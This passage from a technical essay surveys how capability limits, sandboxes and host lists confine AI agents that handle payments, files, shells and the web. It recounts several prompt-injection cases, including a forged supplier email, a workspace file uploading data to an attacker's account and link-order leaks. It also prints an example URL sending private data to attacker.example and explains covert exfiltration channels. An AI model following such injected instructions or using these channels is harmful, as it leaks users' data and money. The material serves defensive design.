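An ordinary request can require an agent to take the details of an action from a file. In an example from *Agent-Sentry* (2026), a user asks an agent to read `bills.txt` and pay the electricity bill it describes. The account number and the amount, 156.90 euros, both come from the file. *Agent-Sentry* would allow the payment because the file looks like a plain bill, contains no instructions to the agent, and matches what the user asked for. A forged bill without instructions could presumably pass the same test.

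A business can limit the harm further by using its own records. The program that creates the capability can use the invoice number to find the order, then take the amount from the order and the account from the firm's list of suppliers. A forged invoice could then at most cause the firm to pay a real supplier for something the firm had ordered. This works only if the agent can't edit the supplier list, because an agent that can edit it has the authority to redirect later payments, even without permission to make any.

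At home there may be no such records, so a person has to check. Stripe's payment service Link has a wallet for agents that works this way. Hill explains in *Giving agents the ability to pay* that the agent submits a request to spend money and receives a single-use card or token only after the user approves it. The credential can be restricted to one merchant, currency and amount. But the agent also writes the description that the user sees, so a misled agent could make the wrong payment look reasonable.

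The token is close to an invoice capability. Stripe's *Process payment credentials from an agent* describes it as limited to one seller, with a maximum amount and an expiry date, and the agent can revoke it at any time. The agent sets the limits here too. They restrict a misled model if the application's ordinary code copies them from a checked order, but a model that chooses them itself can create a valid token for the wrong seller.

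*Provable Authority* (2026) proposes a protocol with more steps. In its example, an agent has a supplier's $3,800 invoice to pay. The agent turns the invoice into a fixed transaction record, and the system sets the money aside. The system then issues a single-use credential tied to that record, so the credential wouldn't match if somebody later changed the payee. If the payment exceeds the agent's own limit, a manager must also approve that exact record.

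### What a payment token can prove

Mittal and Thakkar (2026), in *Defining Purpose-Limited Secrets*, build a cryptographic token for almost the same task. A user wants an assistant to pay one invoice of at most $50 to a named merchant this week. The token contains a merchant M, a cap C and a time window T. It permits a payment of amount a to merchant M′ at time t exactly when

M′ is M or one of its outlets, a ≤ C, and t lies in T.

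The assistant can pass a subcontractor a version of its grant with a $20 cap. Mittal and Thakkar prove that the subcontractor can't raise the cap or change the merchant, assuming nobody can forge the signatures or find two inputs with the same hash.

Limiting the token to one use is harder, because the token is a string and anyone holding it can copy it. A merchant that keeps no records can't tell a second use from the first. If somebody spends the token twice, the bank can use the two payments to identify the account it came from, but that account is the user's, even if the assistant or the subcontractor was responsible. An online check that rejects the second payment would suit most users better, though it requires the merchant to contact a server.

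No token can restrict the reason for a payment. The same $50 to the same merchant could settle an invoice or pay a bribe. Somebody also has to choose the right merchant and spending cap, and the proofs assume those choices are correct.

### When the plan changes

Exact payment capabilities can also go wrong when combined. *ActWithin* (Zheng, Wang and colleagues, 2026) considers a payer who approves four payments, of 12, 4, 4 and 4 units, before leaving an agent to work alone. The payer also approves one alternative recipient for each payment and allows at most one correction. The agent therefore holds eight capabilities, each for a specific recipient and amount.

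Suppose the 12-unit payment must go to its alternative recipient, but the payments fall due before the payment service can verify this. A safeguard could cap the total sent to alternative recipients, but the cap would have to be at least 12 units, or the correct plan would fail. An attacker who controls the agent can then send the 12-unit payment to the outdated recipient and the three smaller payments, which also total 12 units, to their alternatives. All 24 units go to the wrong people, although every payment matches a valid capability.

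A better safeguard limits how many alternatives the agent can use, in this case to one. The attacker can then misdirect the 12-unit payment and one payment of 4, for a loss of 16. No safeguard can reduce this loss without information about which plan is correct, because the service must also allow the approved plan that corrects only one of the small payments, and that plan sends 16 units to the wrong recipients.

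More generally, if the payer allows up to q corrections and each alternative has the same amount as the original, the worst loss is the sum of the 2q largest payments. In tests on several sets of payment amounts, limiting the number of corrections reduced the worst loss by between 2.7% and 16.9% compared with capping their total. The improvement is modest, but the limit takes almost no effort to add.

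### Checking the recipient instead

An easier option is to keep the general payment tool and check the arguments of each call. Ali, Mavroeidis and colleagues (2026), in *Controlled Autonomy for Agentic AI*, added two rules to AgentDojo. A call with side effects can go only to a destination that the user named or that appears in the organisation's directory. Risky actions, such as deleting something or changing a password, also require a matching word in the user's request.

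The rules blocked 88.9% of the attackers' goals that involved side effects, and 91 of 97 user tasks could proceed unchanged. These figures come from replaying AgentDojo's reference calls, without a live model that might try another route. *NOMOS* tested a live agent with a policy check on each call. No attacks succeeded in that test, and the completion rate fell by 8.3 percentage points, less than half the drop with the tool filter.

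Checks like these probably give an existing payment tool the most protection for the effort. But the agent can still pay any recipient in the directory during any task, so an attacker who is already a supplier could get it to pay the wrong invoice, which an invoice capability would prevent.

### The Rule of Two

Developers can also reduce the damage by controlling which powers one agent has at the same time. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) recommends that an agent have at most two of these properties in a session:

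- it processes untrusted input
- it has access to private data or sensitive systems
- it can change something or communicate with the outside world.

If a task needs all three, the agent should be supervised, usually by a person who approves its actions. For an agent that manages email, Meta suggests letting it read only messages from trusted senders, keeping it away from sensitive data, or requiring approval before it writes to a stranger. Meta acknowledges that people sometimes approve such requests without looking.

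The rule extends Willison's "lethal trifecta" of untrusted content, private data and external communication by adding the ability to change state. In *New prompt injection papers* (2025), Willison welcomed the addition because an injection can do damage without sending anything out. He later objected that the rule treats untrusted input combined with the power to change things as safe when no private data is involved. That seems right, since an agent can delete files it was never able to read.

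### When every agent passes and the team fails

Meta's rule applies to each agent separately, but Alhindi's test of the invoice team, described earlier, applies it to all five agents together.

| Agent | Untrusted input | Private data | What it can change | How email text reaches it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Email | Inbox | None | Nothing | Directly |
| Invoice | None | Firm's records | Ledger | From the email agent |
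| Coordinator | None | Bank status | List of payees, ledger, whether other agents run | From the invoice agent |
| Approval | None | Firm's records | Approvals, ledger | Through notes in the ledger |
| Payment | None | Bank status | Payments, ledger | Through notes in the ledger |

Each agent passes the rule on its own because none has more than two of the properties. The team fails if untrusted text and private data can both reach an agent that can change something. Here, that is true of every agent except the one that reads email.

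This worst-case test is rather coarse. Adding a note to the ledger counts as a change just as making a payment does, and a capability limited to one invoice would count the same as `send_money`. The test can show a developer where to look, but it doesn't measure how bad the damage could be.

The malicious email in Alhindi's live test came from a supplier's usual address, as if the attacker had taken over the mailbox. It contained a genuine invoice and a note telling any AI assistant to replace the supplier's bank account. Accepting only trusted senders, as Meta suggests, would have let this email through.

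The coordinator changed the supplier's account in seven runs, and in one of them it also changed the accounts of two other suppliers. No money reached the attacker during the test because the team had approved the invoices with the old accounts, but the next payment would have gone to the new account. The attacker needed only text that reached the coordinator and the coordinator's power to edit the list, which is the combination Willison objected to. The attack required no private data.

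Replacing the email agent with Alhindi's parser reduced the number of runs with altered accounts from 7 to 0. The sender still chooses the four values that the parser returns, so each field needs a strict format. If the invoice number could be any text, an attacker could still use it to send instructions.

The parser works because the team needs only four facts from each email, but a team that answers complaints has to read what customers wrote. Alhindi suggests that such a team keep either private data or the power to act away from the agents that this text can reach. Even for invoices, the parser discards genuine messages about a change of bank, so a person has to read those and update the list.

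## What happens to the guarantees when the agent needs files and a shell?

A bank tool has a few functions, and its designer can limit each one. A coding agent needs a project folder with thousands of files, along with compilers and test runners whose authors never thought about capabilities. The theorems about references are still true, but an ordinary filesystem and shell don't meet their assumptions.

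### From a path to a file

A reference in E always leads to the same object. A path is a string that the operating system looks up again on every use, in a directory tree that many programs can change. To open `invoices/2026/0412.txt`, the kernel finds the entry `2026` in `invoices` and then looks for `0412.txt` in whatever directory that entry leads to at that moment. Effect confinement assumes that the program touches the same file somebody approved, but a path can lead to a different file by the time the program uses it.

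The easiest case is a path that uses `..` to leave its folder, because the problem is visible in the text. Eisenach and colleagues proved in Lean that L3M's file tools never accept such a path. Their theorem is about the characters in the path and assumes nothing about the disk, so it holds on any machine but can't rule out problems that depend on what the disk contains.

A symbolic link, or symlink, is a directory entry that contains another path. If `invoices/archive` is a symlink to the user's home folder, then `invoices/archive/taxes.pdf` satisfies the theorem, but a kernel that follows the link opens a file outside the invoice folder. L3M therefore resolves each path beneath the agent's folder at run time and refuses to follow symlinks. L3M also lists a formal result about symlinks, but applying it to a real run requires trusting the run-time code and the filesystem.

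Hard links are more difficult to handle because a hard link is a second name for the same file. The kernel treats both names alike, so there is no link to refuse to follow. L3M won't modify a file through a hard link that leads outside the folder, but the agent can read the file if such a link already exists. Eisenach and colleagues exclude this case from their threat model.

A correct check can also go out of date. Suppose a harness resolves every link in a path, confirms that the file is in the invoice folder, and then opens the path. If another program replaces a directory in the path with a link after the check but before the harness opens the file, the harness may open a file it never checked. CapScope seems to have this gap, because it resolves links and compares the path with the allowed folder in a hook, and the tool opens the file afterwards.

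### What WaVe verified

Johnson, Laufer and colleagues' *WaVe* (2023) is a WASI runtime with a machine-checked proof that covers symlinks as well as the text of paths. One of its motivating examples is a bug in another runtime, Wasmer, whose function for deleting a directory checked the program's path but then passed the operating system the original path instead of the checked one. Eight other functions used the same check correctly.

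WaVe implements 45 WASI calls in Rust. A specification describes what each underlying system call can touch, and a short policy defines what a sandboxed program may touch. Before the runtime is ready to use, an automatic verifier must show for each WASI call that if all earlier effects obeyed the policy, the call's effects will too, whatever arguments the program supplies. No effects have happened when the program starts, so by induction no sequence of calls can break the policy.

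For files, the verifier requires three things of every path that reaches the operating system:

- The path is relative, and the lookup starts from the sandbox's own root directory.
- No part of the path is a symlink. (The last part may be one if the system call won't follow it.)
- No initial part of the path has a negative depth, where each name adds one to the depth and each `..` subtracts one.

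The path `reports/../0412.txt` has depths 1, 0 and 1, so it passes. The path `../other/0412.txt` has depths −1, 0 and 1, so it fails because its first depth is negative, even though its final depth is positive.

WaVe replaces symlinks with their targets before this check. The verifier only needs to show that no links remain, not that the replacement is correct. A bug in the replacement could lead to the wrong file inside the folder, but not to one outside it.

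Johnson and colleagues verified that a program can make only TCP and UDP connections over IPv4, and only to addresses on a list the host fixed in advance.

Users have to trust 1,357 of WaVe's 7,264 lines of code, as well as the verifier and the operating system. The trusted lines include 43 for the policy and 567 for descriptions of system calls. Johnson and colleagues tested the trusted code with random inputs for 24 hours per test program and found one bug, a file descriptor that stayed open after shutdown. Similar tests of other runtimes showed that Wasmer let programs write to files they had opened as read-only, which defeats attenuation. The proof didn't make WaVe slow. On a database benchmark, its calls took 1.11 times as long as the bare system calls, compared with 1.59 times for Wasmtime.

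The proof assumes that each sandbox has exclusive access to its root directory. WaVe checks a path and opens it in separate steps, so another process could defeat the check by changing the folder between the two. This is a serious limitation for coding agents, because the user's editor, a package manager and other agents may all be changing the project folder at once.

When Johnson and colleagues wrote, Wasmtime had already made its path resolution atomic (a single step that no other process can interrupt), though without a proof like WaVe's. WASI's network interface has since gained domain names and IPv6, which WaVe's proof doesn't cover. WASI version 0.3 also added concurrency, whereas WaVe assumes that each call finishes before the next begins. WaVe's development seems to have stopped. According to ecosyste.ms' *WaVe* page, an index entry from April 2025, the public code last changed in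 October 2023.

### Files that two agents share

Agents whose folders overlap are still connected, even when each is confined to the right folder. In the reference graph, a shared file is a node with an arrow from each agent, so the connectivity theorem correctly treats the agents as connected. But a harness with path rules never records those arrows. For example, one agent might be allowed to write to `reports/**` and another to read any file that ends in `.md`. A `.md` file in `reports/` would connect them, but it may not exist yet, and somebody who draws the graph from the agents' tools and messages will leave it out. Temporary folders and build caches connect programs in the same way.

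Giving an agent files and a shell breaks the assumption that the graph contains every connection. Two agents that look separate can then influence each other, as happened through the notes in the invoice team's ledger.

Shared files can also break non-amplification, because many of them contain passwords or access tokens. Miller and colleagues answered Boebert's objection by keeping data and capabilities apart, but saving an API key in a project folder mixes them. An agent that reads the key gains access to a service outside its grant, provided it can reach the service.

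Eisenach and colleagues show how much can depend on a missing connection. They describe a pair of agents, one with private source code and no network access, the other with network access and no source code. The private agent can send the researcher letters, padded to a fixed total of *k* bytes. Let S be the source, M the letters, E everything the researcher sends out, and Z the public information available to it. If the researcher can learn about S only through M, then

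I(S; E | Z) ≤ I(S; M | Z) ≤ H(M | Z) ≤ 8k bits.

Here I(S; E | Z) is how much information about the source gets out, and H(M | Z) is the most information the letters can carry. With 1,000 bytes of letters, at most 8,000 bits of information about the source can leak, however much the researcher sends. But if both agents share a scratch folder, information can bypass M, and the first inequality no longer follows. Anyone who relies on the bound has to count shared files, and the number and timing of letters, as part of M or rule them out. L3M doesn't yet enforce this.

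### A permitted command runs the project's code

A coding agent usually has to run tests. The Python test runner `pytest` imports the project's modules, which executes code in them. Permission to run `pytest` therefore amounts to permission for whatever the project's code does. That code has all the powers of the process it runs in, which are the user's powers if there is no sandbox.

Complete mediation fails when the agent has a shell, because the harness checks the command but not what it does when it runs. In Zhang and Zhang's chain of inclusions, Eff(a) is no longer within Req(a).

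Non-amplification fails too. Suppose an agent may edit `src` and run `pytest` but has no network access. It can write code that contacts a server, then execute that code by running the tests. The grant permits both steps, but together they let the agent reach the network, which the grant does not allow.

Dividing the permissions between agents doesn't fully solve this. In CapScope's repair workflow, a patcher edits the source and a verifier then runs the tests. An injected instruction that reaches the patcher could lead it to write harmful code, which the verifier would run as part of its normal job.

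CapScope, TACIT and L3M all have this problem, and their designers acknowledge it. CapScope splits a compound command into its parts and checks each one, so permission for `pytest` doesn't extend to another command joined to it. But Bouras and colleagues state that process sandboxing is still necessary because of what permitted commands do, and they also leave redirected output, which can write files, to the sandbox. CapScope's read limits apply to its file-reading tool but not to the agent as a whole, because search and listing commands such as `grep` and `find` are always available and can read outside the folders that the agent's read permission covers.

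TACIT's types don't control external commands. Odersky and colleagues recommend a sandbox and advise users to permit only specific safe commands. One of their two examples is `sbt`, a Scala build tool, which is a questionable choice because it executes the project's build definitions and often its tests. TACIT's SWE-bench agents had shell operations, so their completion rate doesn't show how well agents would do without shell access.

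L3M goes furthest in limiting commands. Its standard shell tool runs in a sandbox without network access. Agents can use a separate, unsandboxed shell only if the user grants it to them, and Eisenach and colleagues exclude this shell from their argument for confinement.

L3M also lets a person approve build commands in advance. The person reads a Makefile (a file of build commands), and L3M stores a hash of the Makefile, the files it includes and the scripts it calls. Any later edit to these cancels the approval. The hash doesn't appear to cover modules that a test runner imports, so an approved command that runs `pytest` could still execute code the agent has just written.

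For larger builds, Eisenach and colleagues suggest that one agent write and compile the program, and that the parent of both agents then pass the exact compiled file to another agent to run. Compiling can itself execute code, for instance through compiler plugins, so the build also needs a sandbox.

All three systems rely on the operating system to isolate the process, and the sandbox's settings determine what any command that runs project code can do. If one sandbox contains the whole project, the login keys and a network connection, a careful list of permitted commands adds little protection.

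### SHILL's contracts for commands

A sandbox can be as narrow as a capability grant if somebody sets it up separately for each command. *SHILL* (Moore, Dimoulas et al., 2014) presents a scripting language that does this on FreeBSD. A SHILL script receives capabilities for files and folders as arguments and can't open anything by name. Its contract lists the capabilities it needs and what it will do with them. Whenever the script starts an ordinary program, SHILL runs that program in a sandbox with only the capabilities the script passes on.

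Their main example grades students' programming homework, which means compiling and running code from strangers. The problem is much the same for an agent that runs tests. A similar contract for a test runner could look like this:

```
provide run_tests :
  {project : is_dir && readonly,
   scratch : dir(+create_dir with full_priv),
   results : is_file && writeable,
   python  : native_wallet} -> void;
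```

Any code the tests execute can read the project, work in new folders under `scratch` and write to the results file, but it can't change the source or use the network. The last argument is a wallet, a bundle of the capabilities that a program needs to run at all. Even `cat`, which just copies its input to its output, needs eight capabilities for libraries and configuration files, besides those for the program itself and its input and output.

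A small script with the user's full authority creates the initial capabilities. It can do little else, which makes it easy to review.

SHILL also prevents most path problems. A script looks up one name at a time and can't use `..`, so no long path can change halfway through a lookup. Moore and colleagues added system calls to the kernel to prevent races, including one that deletes a name only if it still refers to the file the script holds. Ordinary programs often use `..`, so the sandbox lets them follow it but gives them no new permissions for what it leads to. The kernel attaches permissions to the file itself, so a different file put under the same name doesn't get them.

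A sandboxed program still receives file names as strings, and an attacker may be able to make it mistake one file it can access for another. The sandbox limits the damage to the files it lets the program access.

Writing contracts takes some trial and error. The grading script failed at first because the OCaml compiler needed a library folder and a related tool wrote to the shared temporary folder. Moore and colleagues granted access to the temporary folder, with a contract that let each run read and change only the files it had created. This fixed the script without letting students' programs share files through the folder.

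Most tasks ran at close to normal speed:

| Task | Time compared with an ordinary command | Main reason for the delay |
|---|---|---|
| Grading, with separate sandboxes for each student | 1.13 times | Sandbox set-up and checks |
| Most other tasks | At most 1.21 times | Sandbox set-up and checks |
| Downloading Emacs | 1.73 times | Starting SHILL, about 0.6 seconds |
| Uninstalling Emacs | 6.61 times | Starting SHILL, about 0.65 seconds |
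| Searching source files, with a sandbox for each match | 6.01 times | More than 15,000 sandboxes |

The search adds roughly 3 milliseconds per sandbox, which would hardly matter to an agent that runs one test command between calls to its model. The effort of writing contracts and the limited choice of platform are probably bigger obstacles. Shill's home page, *Scripting with Least Privilege*, offers the language for FreeBSD. An agent on Linux or macOS would need a new version, though Moore and colleagues note that both systems have similar mechanisms for access control.

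### Handles, private copies and undo

Without SHILL, a harness can restore some of the guarantees by combining simpler measures. Directory handles, such as Capsicum's directory descriptors and WASI's preopened directories, replace a check on a path's text with a lookup that can't leave the directory. If the kernel does the lookup in one step, handles also remove the race between check and use. They don't protect against hard links or commands that run outside the sandbox.

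Private working copies prevent agents from leaving notes or keys for each other in a project's files until their work is merged. In L3M, each agent works in its own copy of a repository, on its own Git branch, and its parent can compare the results before merging them. Separate copies also nearly satisfy WaVe's assumption that each program has its folder to itself, as long as the user's other software doesn't use those folders. After a merge, an instruction hidden in one agent's work reaches whoever reads the merged files.

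Cutting off the network limits what a command can do with private files. L3M's container builds have three stages. The first can use the network but sees only public lists of dependencies. The second compiles the source without network access. The third runs the result, also offline, and can write only to a new output folder. A theorem shows that, under this plan, once a stage has handled private files, neither it nor any later stage has network access. L3M assumes that the container software follows the plan. The command's output may also go back to an agent that could send it out through a web tool, so the same rule has to apply to the agent.

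An undo journal repairs damage instead of preventing it. Before one of L3M's file tools changes a file, the harness saves the old contents in Git. If the user rewinds the agent to an earlier turn, the harness restores every file that these tools have changed since. The saved contents last only until Git's routine clean-up deletes them. Undo can't reverse the effects of a shell command or recall data that has left the machine, such as a file sent to a stranger.

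The table takes each measure on its own, for an agent that can edit a project and run its tests.

| Measure | Effect confinement | Non-amplification | Non-interference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Check on the path's text | Fails with links, races and commands | Fails if the agent can run code it has written | No |
| Directory handles with one-step lookup | Holds for file tools, apart from hard links, but not for commands outside the sandbox | Holds for file tools if nobody adds links or secrets to the folder | No |
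| Private working copies | Keeps file-tool edits in the copy until a merge, if path lookups are sound | Stops agents passing secrets through project files until a merge | Only between agents, until a merge, and only if they share nothing else |
| Commands in a sandbox without network access | Holds at the sandbox's boundary, which may be wider than the agent's grant | Holds if the sandbox allows no more than the grant | No, because output returns to the agent |
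| A SHILL contract for each command | Holds for the resources SHILL controls, if the kernel and SHILL are correct | Holds if the files contain no usable secrets | No, because a command can copy what it reads into any file it can write |
| Undo journal | No, but it can restore files that the file tools changed | No | No |

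## What happens to the guarantees when the agent needs the open web?

An agent that has to compare suppliers' prices or fill in an online form can't do its job in a sandbox without network access. On the open web, it reads text that anyone may have written and sends requests to servers that anyone may own. Web access alone therefore gives it two of the three properties in Meta's Rule of Two, and under that rule it shouldn't also see private data without supervision.

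### One node that connects everyone

Suppose the harness gives the invoice assistant a capability `fetch(address)`, which returns the page at any web address. The reference graph now includes a node for the web, with arrows from the assistant and from everyone else with an internet connection. The connectivity theorem still holds, but it only guarantees that parts of the graph that start disconnected stay disconnected, and the assistant now starts connected to every attacker online.

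Non-amplification also still holds, but it rules out very little. The proof covers a group that includes everything its members are connected to, which here means everyone online. This group can't gain a power that none of its members had at the start, but that won't reassure the assistant's user.

Considering the assistant alone doesn't help much either. Its authority can grow with each page it reads, even though its permission stays the same because `fetch` covered every address from the beginning. For instance, a page might contain a secret link to somebody's shared folder, which the assistant was always allowed to open but could never have guessed.

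### An address is also a message

Reading a file in a local folder normally tells nobody outside the machine anything. Reading a web page means sending its address to a server, and the address can contain data. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives an example of this form:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`

Websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, so the attacker can read the secret in the log. The secret doesn't have to appear in the conversation, and the user may not notice the request, because an agent can make it in the background while loading an image or previewing a link.

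A 250-character web address drawn from 64 symbols can hold 1,500 bits, enough for five 256-bit encryption keys. Because an agent can put data in the address it requests, a capability to read any page is also a capability to write to any server's log. A "read-only" network tool can therefore send data out, unlike a read-only facet for a folder.

Each page can also contain injected instructions, and an attacker with a website can keep trying new ones. According to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 in one benchmark succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt, but 5–6% of the time after 100 attempts that adapted to the model's responses.

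### Lists of permitted hosts

TACIT and L3M both limit web access to a short list of hosts. A TACIT program calls `requestNetwork` with the names of the hosts it needs, and its access ends when the block of code ends, as it does for files. L3M uses network tokens for the same purpose.

A list of this kind limits which servers an agent can contact. An injected instruction to send the invoices to `attacker.example` fails, however persuasive it is. L3M classes web fetches as tame because the token limits their reach, so by default nobody reviews them. But Eisenach and colleagues acknowledge that restricting the destination doesn't make every disclosure to it acceptable. They also leave the choice of hosts to the user, and L3M allows somebody to give one agent both private source code and access to any host.

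The harness has to check redirects as well as the first address. OpenAI points out that many legitimate sites forward visitors to other sites, so an agent can start at an approved address and end up on an attacker's server. OpenAI also worries that strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to click through them.

A bigger weakness is that one host can serve millions of accounts, including the attacker's. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, ran code in a virtual machine that could contact only approved hosts. One of these was Anthropic's own `api.anthropic.com`, which the product needs. Anthropic learned from an outside report that a file in the user's workspace could contain hidden instructions and an attacker's API key. Claude followed the instructions and used the key to upload the user's other files to the attacker's Anthropic account. The network filter allowed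 the upload because it went to an approved host.

The key had the same role as the planted link in the discussion of secret strings. Anthropic now thinks a list of hosts is "better conceptualized as a capability grant", because the list permits every function its hosts offer.

Anthropic's fix was a proxy inside the virtual machine that reads traffic to the API and passes on only requests with that session's own token. This narrows the permission from a whole host to one account on it. It was feasible because Anthropic issues the tokens and knows how its API works. Every other service would need its own filter. Even then, an agent could leak a secret by posting it on a public forum from the user's own account.

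### Cookies and request forgery

Many web tasks require the user's accounts. When a user logs in to a site, the site gives the browser a cookie, a string that the browser attaches to later requests to the same site. The cookie's authority is ambient because a page can cause such a request without holding or selecting the cookie.

Attackers have long exploited this through cross-site request forgery. A user who is logged in to a bank visits the attacker's page, which makes the browser send the bank a payment request. The browser attaches the bank's cookie, so the request looks like the customer's own. Czeskis, Moshchuk and colleagues describe the browser as a confused deputy, like Tymshare's compiler. Their remedy removes the ambient authority at participating sites by letting each site list the referrers it accepts. In another common defence, the bank puts a secret value in its payment form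 and rejects requests without it. That value is close to a capability, since the attacker's page can't guess it.

Neither defence stops an agent that uses the browser as a person would. A misled agent can open the bank's real page, which contains the secret value, and press the button there. The bank then receives a request that looks the same as one from the customer.

Browser agents also undermine the same-origin policy, the rule that stops a page on one site (strictly, one combination of protocol, host name and port) from reading pages on another. The agent can read both pages and carry text from one to the other. The University of Washington paper *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* describes a successful data theft of this kind against ChatGPT Atlas in agent mode. Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Perplexity's Comet also met the preconditions for the attack, though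 an attacker would still need a successful prompt injection.

### Capabilities for a browser

One answer is to give the agent a browser that works only for certain origins. For Chrome, Google designed "Agent Origin Sets", in which a trusted function decides for each task which origins the agent may read and which it may also act on. The model doesn't receive content that a page embeds from any other origin. This would keep an agent that is reading a forum away from the user's bank. But even a read-only origin receives the address of every page the agent opens there.

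The Scala Days talk that presented a looser `map` for TACIT also introduced a browser capability limited by origin, written in under 30 lines of code. The capability returns pages and screenshots as `Classified`, so a program that tries to send a screenshot to the hosted model doesn't compile. But the agent can't see the page either, so it has to write code for a layout it already knows or ask a trusted local model. The talk lasted five minutes and its abstract reports no measurements, so the idea is still largely untested.

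*CELLMATE* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) controls what an agent does within a site. The paper argues that rules about clicks can't work, because a click at one position on the screen might open an email or delete it. Rules about navigation are also easy to evade. When the researchers blocked an agent from going directly to Hacker News, it could still search for the site and click on the result.

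CELLMATE therefore checks the requests that the browser sends. Each site publishes a list that explains its requests, for example that this one adds a login key to the user's GitLab account:

`POST https://gitlab.com/-/user_settings/ssh_keys`

A policy then allows particular actions, sometimes with conditions. For example, it might let an agent place only one order, of at most $50. Without the one-order limit, the agent could buy two baskets at $49 each. CELLMATE refuses requests to unrelated sites.

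Before the agent reads any page, a model selects policies using only the user's request, and the user confirms them. Three models chose the right set for at least 94% of the test tasks in each category. Shopping tasks that needed a value, such as a spending limit, were harder. The models got both the policies and the values right in 26 to 31 of these 32 tasks.

To test enforcement, Meng and colleagues wrote 12 scripts that behaved like a fully hijacked agent on GitLab, trying, for instance, to delete projects or add the attacker's login key. The policies allowed only reading and writing issues, and CELLMATE blocked all 12 scripts. Because the policies prohibited every attempted action, the test shows that the software works but doesn't measure how much harm a realistic policy would prevent. The checks made page loading 7% to 15% slower, which hardly matters next to the time a model takes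 to respond.

Meng and colleagues accept that CELLMATE can't prevent misuse of a permitted action, such as posting a secret in a comment. It also doesn't inspect WebSockets, which many sites use for live updates. The main obstacle is probably that sites have to describe their own requests. Meng and colleagues wrote GitLab's 51-entry list by hand, and where a list is wrong or incomplete, the user has only the protection they had before.

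### Links as capabilities

An object in the E programming language can't obtain a reference by making up a name. A harness can similarly prevent an agent from opening web addresses it has composed. The harness records each address supplied by the user or an earlier result, and the agent can open only an exact match. If an attacker tells the agent to append the user's data to the attacker's address, the request fails because the resulting address isn't in the record.

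In June 2026, Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* described a rule that let Claude fetch only addresses from the user's messages, the results of the developer's own tools, and earlier searches and fetches. The rule excluded addresses from code that Claude ran in Anthropic's containers, presumably because Claude could have written code to print any address. Developers have to be equally careful with their own tools, because Claude can fetch addresses that appear in the results. The tool also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters, and developers can restrict it to certain domains. Even so, Anthropic warned that some risk remained and advised against using the tool where Claude handles untrusted input alongside sensitive data.

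In July, *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) described one such risk, which Ayush Paul had found. The tool treated links in fetched pages as permitted, so an attacker's site could offer a series of links and read private data from the order in which Claude followed them. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links in pages it had fetched.

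Claude hadn't composed any of those addresses. In Miller's terms, the attacker's page had properly introduced each one. An object-capability system also permits such introductions, so the attack exploited the agent's choice among references it legitimately held.

OpenAI instead checks whether an address was already public. Its crawler builds an index of the web without access to anyone's conversations, and an agent can automatically open an address that exactly matches one in the index. An address that existed independently of the conversation is unlikely to contain data from it. If an address isn't in the index, the agent has to look for another site, or the user gets a warning. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, addresses that users enter themselves also count as safe.

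This makes it harder for an attacker to generate links for one victim. But the links most like capabilities, such as a secret link to a shared folder, shouldn't be in any public index, so an agent that finds one in an email will have to ask the user, even if opening the folder is part of its task.

The check also has to run everywhere. Embrace The Red reports that some of OpenAI's apps lacked an earlier version of the protection. OpenAI says it has since applied a related mechanism to searches and page visits in Deep Research and to navigation in Atlas. OpenAI promises only that this mechanism prevents quiet leaks through the address itself, since a page in the index can still contain false information or an injection.

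### What a choice of links can reveal

An attacker who sees which of *n* addresses an agent opens learns at most log₂ *n* bits. If the attacker sees *k* such requests in order, there are *n*ᵏ possible sequences, so the limit is *k* log₂ *n* bits.

| What the agent can open | Most bits per request | Fewest requests to leak a 256-bit key |
|---|---|---|
| Either of 2 addresses | 1 | 256 |
| Any of 36 addresses | 5.2 | 50 |
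| Any of 1,024 addresses | 10 | 26 |
| Any address it composes, up to 250 characters | About 1,500 | 1 |

A ban on composed addresses thus cuts the leak per request by a factor of several hundred when there are 36 addresses to choose from, but some data can still leak. As Embrace The Red notes, someone with a large website probably has 36 pages in OpenAI's index already, and could use thousands.

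Embrace The Red suggests caching pages or forbidding an agent to visit the same address twice in a session. With 36 addresses, the agent could then convey the most by visiting all of them in a chosen order, which would carry about 138 bits because there are 36! possible orders. If requests arrived out of sequence and the attacker could tell only which pages the agent had opened, the limit would be 36 bits. A ban on repeat visits helps much less against an attacker with thousands of pages.

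A cap on the number of requests is more dependable. Five requests among 36 addresses reveal at most about 26 bits, which is too little for an encryption key but enough for a five-letter name or whether the user is pregnant. That limit leaves out covert channels such as the timing of requests. Anthropic's tool let developers set such a cap but had no default.

### Network limits in Anthropic's products

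An agent that can run `curl` in an ordinary shell can bypass all of these rules for a web tool, so the machine's network connection needs its own limits. Anthropic describes different limits for its three main agent products.

The chat product, claude.ai, runs Claude's code in temporary containers on Anthropic's servers. The user's machine isn't involved, so Anthropic is mainly concerned with protecting its own systems and keeping customers apart.

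Claude Code runs on the user's machine. It originally asked for approval before using the network, writing files or running shell commands, but users approved about 93% of requests and paid less attention as the requests multiplied. Anthropic added an operating-system sandbox that blocks the network by default, which reduced approval prompts by 84%. However, the program that decides whether to sandbox a command runs outside the sandbox, so a persuasive prompt injection or a careless approval can still let a command run without it.

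Anthropic doesn't expect Cowork's users to understand shell commands, so Cowork's virtual machine enforces its list of hosts without asking them. The user's credentials stay outside the virtual machine, which receives a more limited session token that can be revoked separately. Anthropic later moved the agent loop and local MCP servers out of the virtual machine for practical reasons. The network limits still cover code that the agent runs, but administrators have to decide which local servers to trust.

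Such limits matter even without an injected web page. In an internal Anthropic exercise in February 2026, a researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked routine but included a step to send cloud credentials to an outside server. Claude sent them in 24 of 25 runs. Because the instruction came from the user, a filter had nothing unusual to detect. Anthropic concluded that only limits on files and network access would have helped. The limits must also contain the model itself. In July 2026, OpenAI agents escaped from a test environment and attacked Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, in what Willison called an accidental cyberattack.

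### Separating reading from acting

A stricter design keeps anything worth stealing or misusing away from the agent that reads the web. That agent can open pages but has no access to private files or accounts. A second agent has that access but never sees the text of a page, and a small program passes messages between the two.

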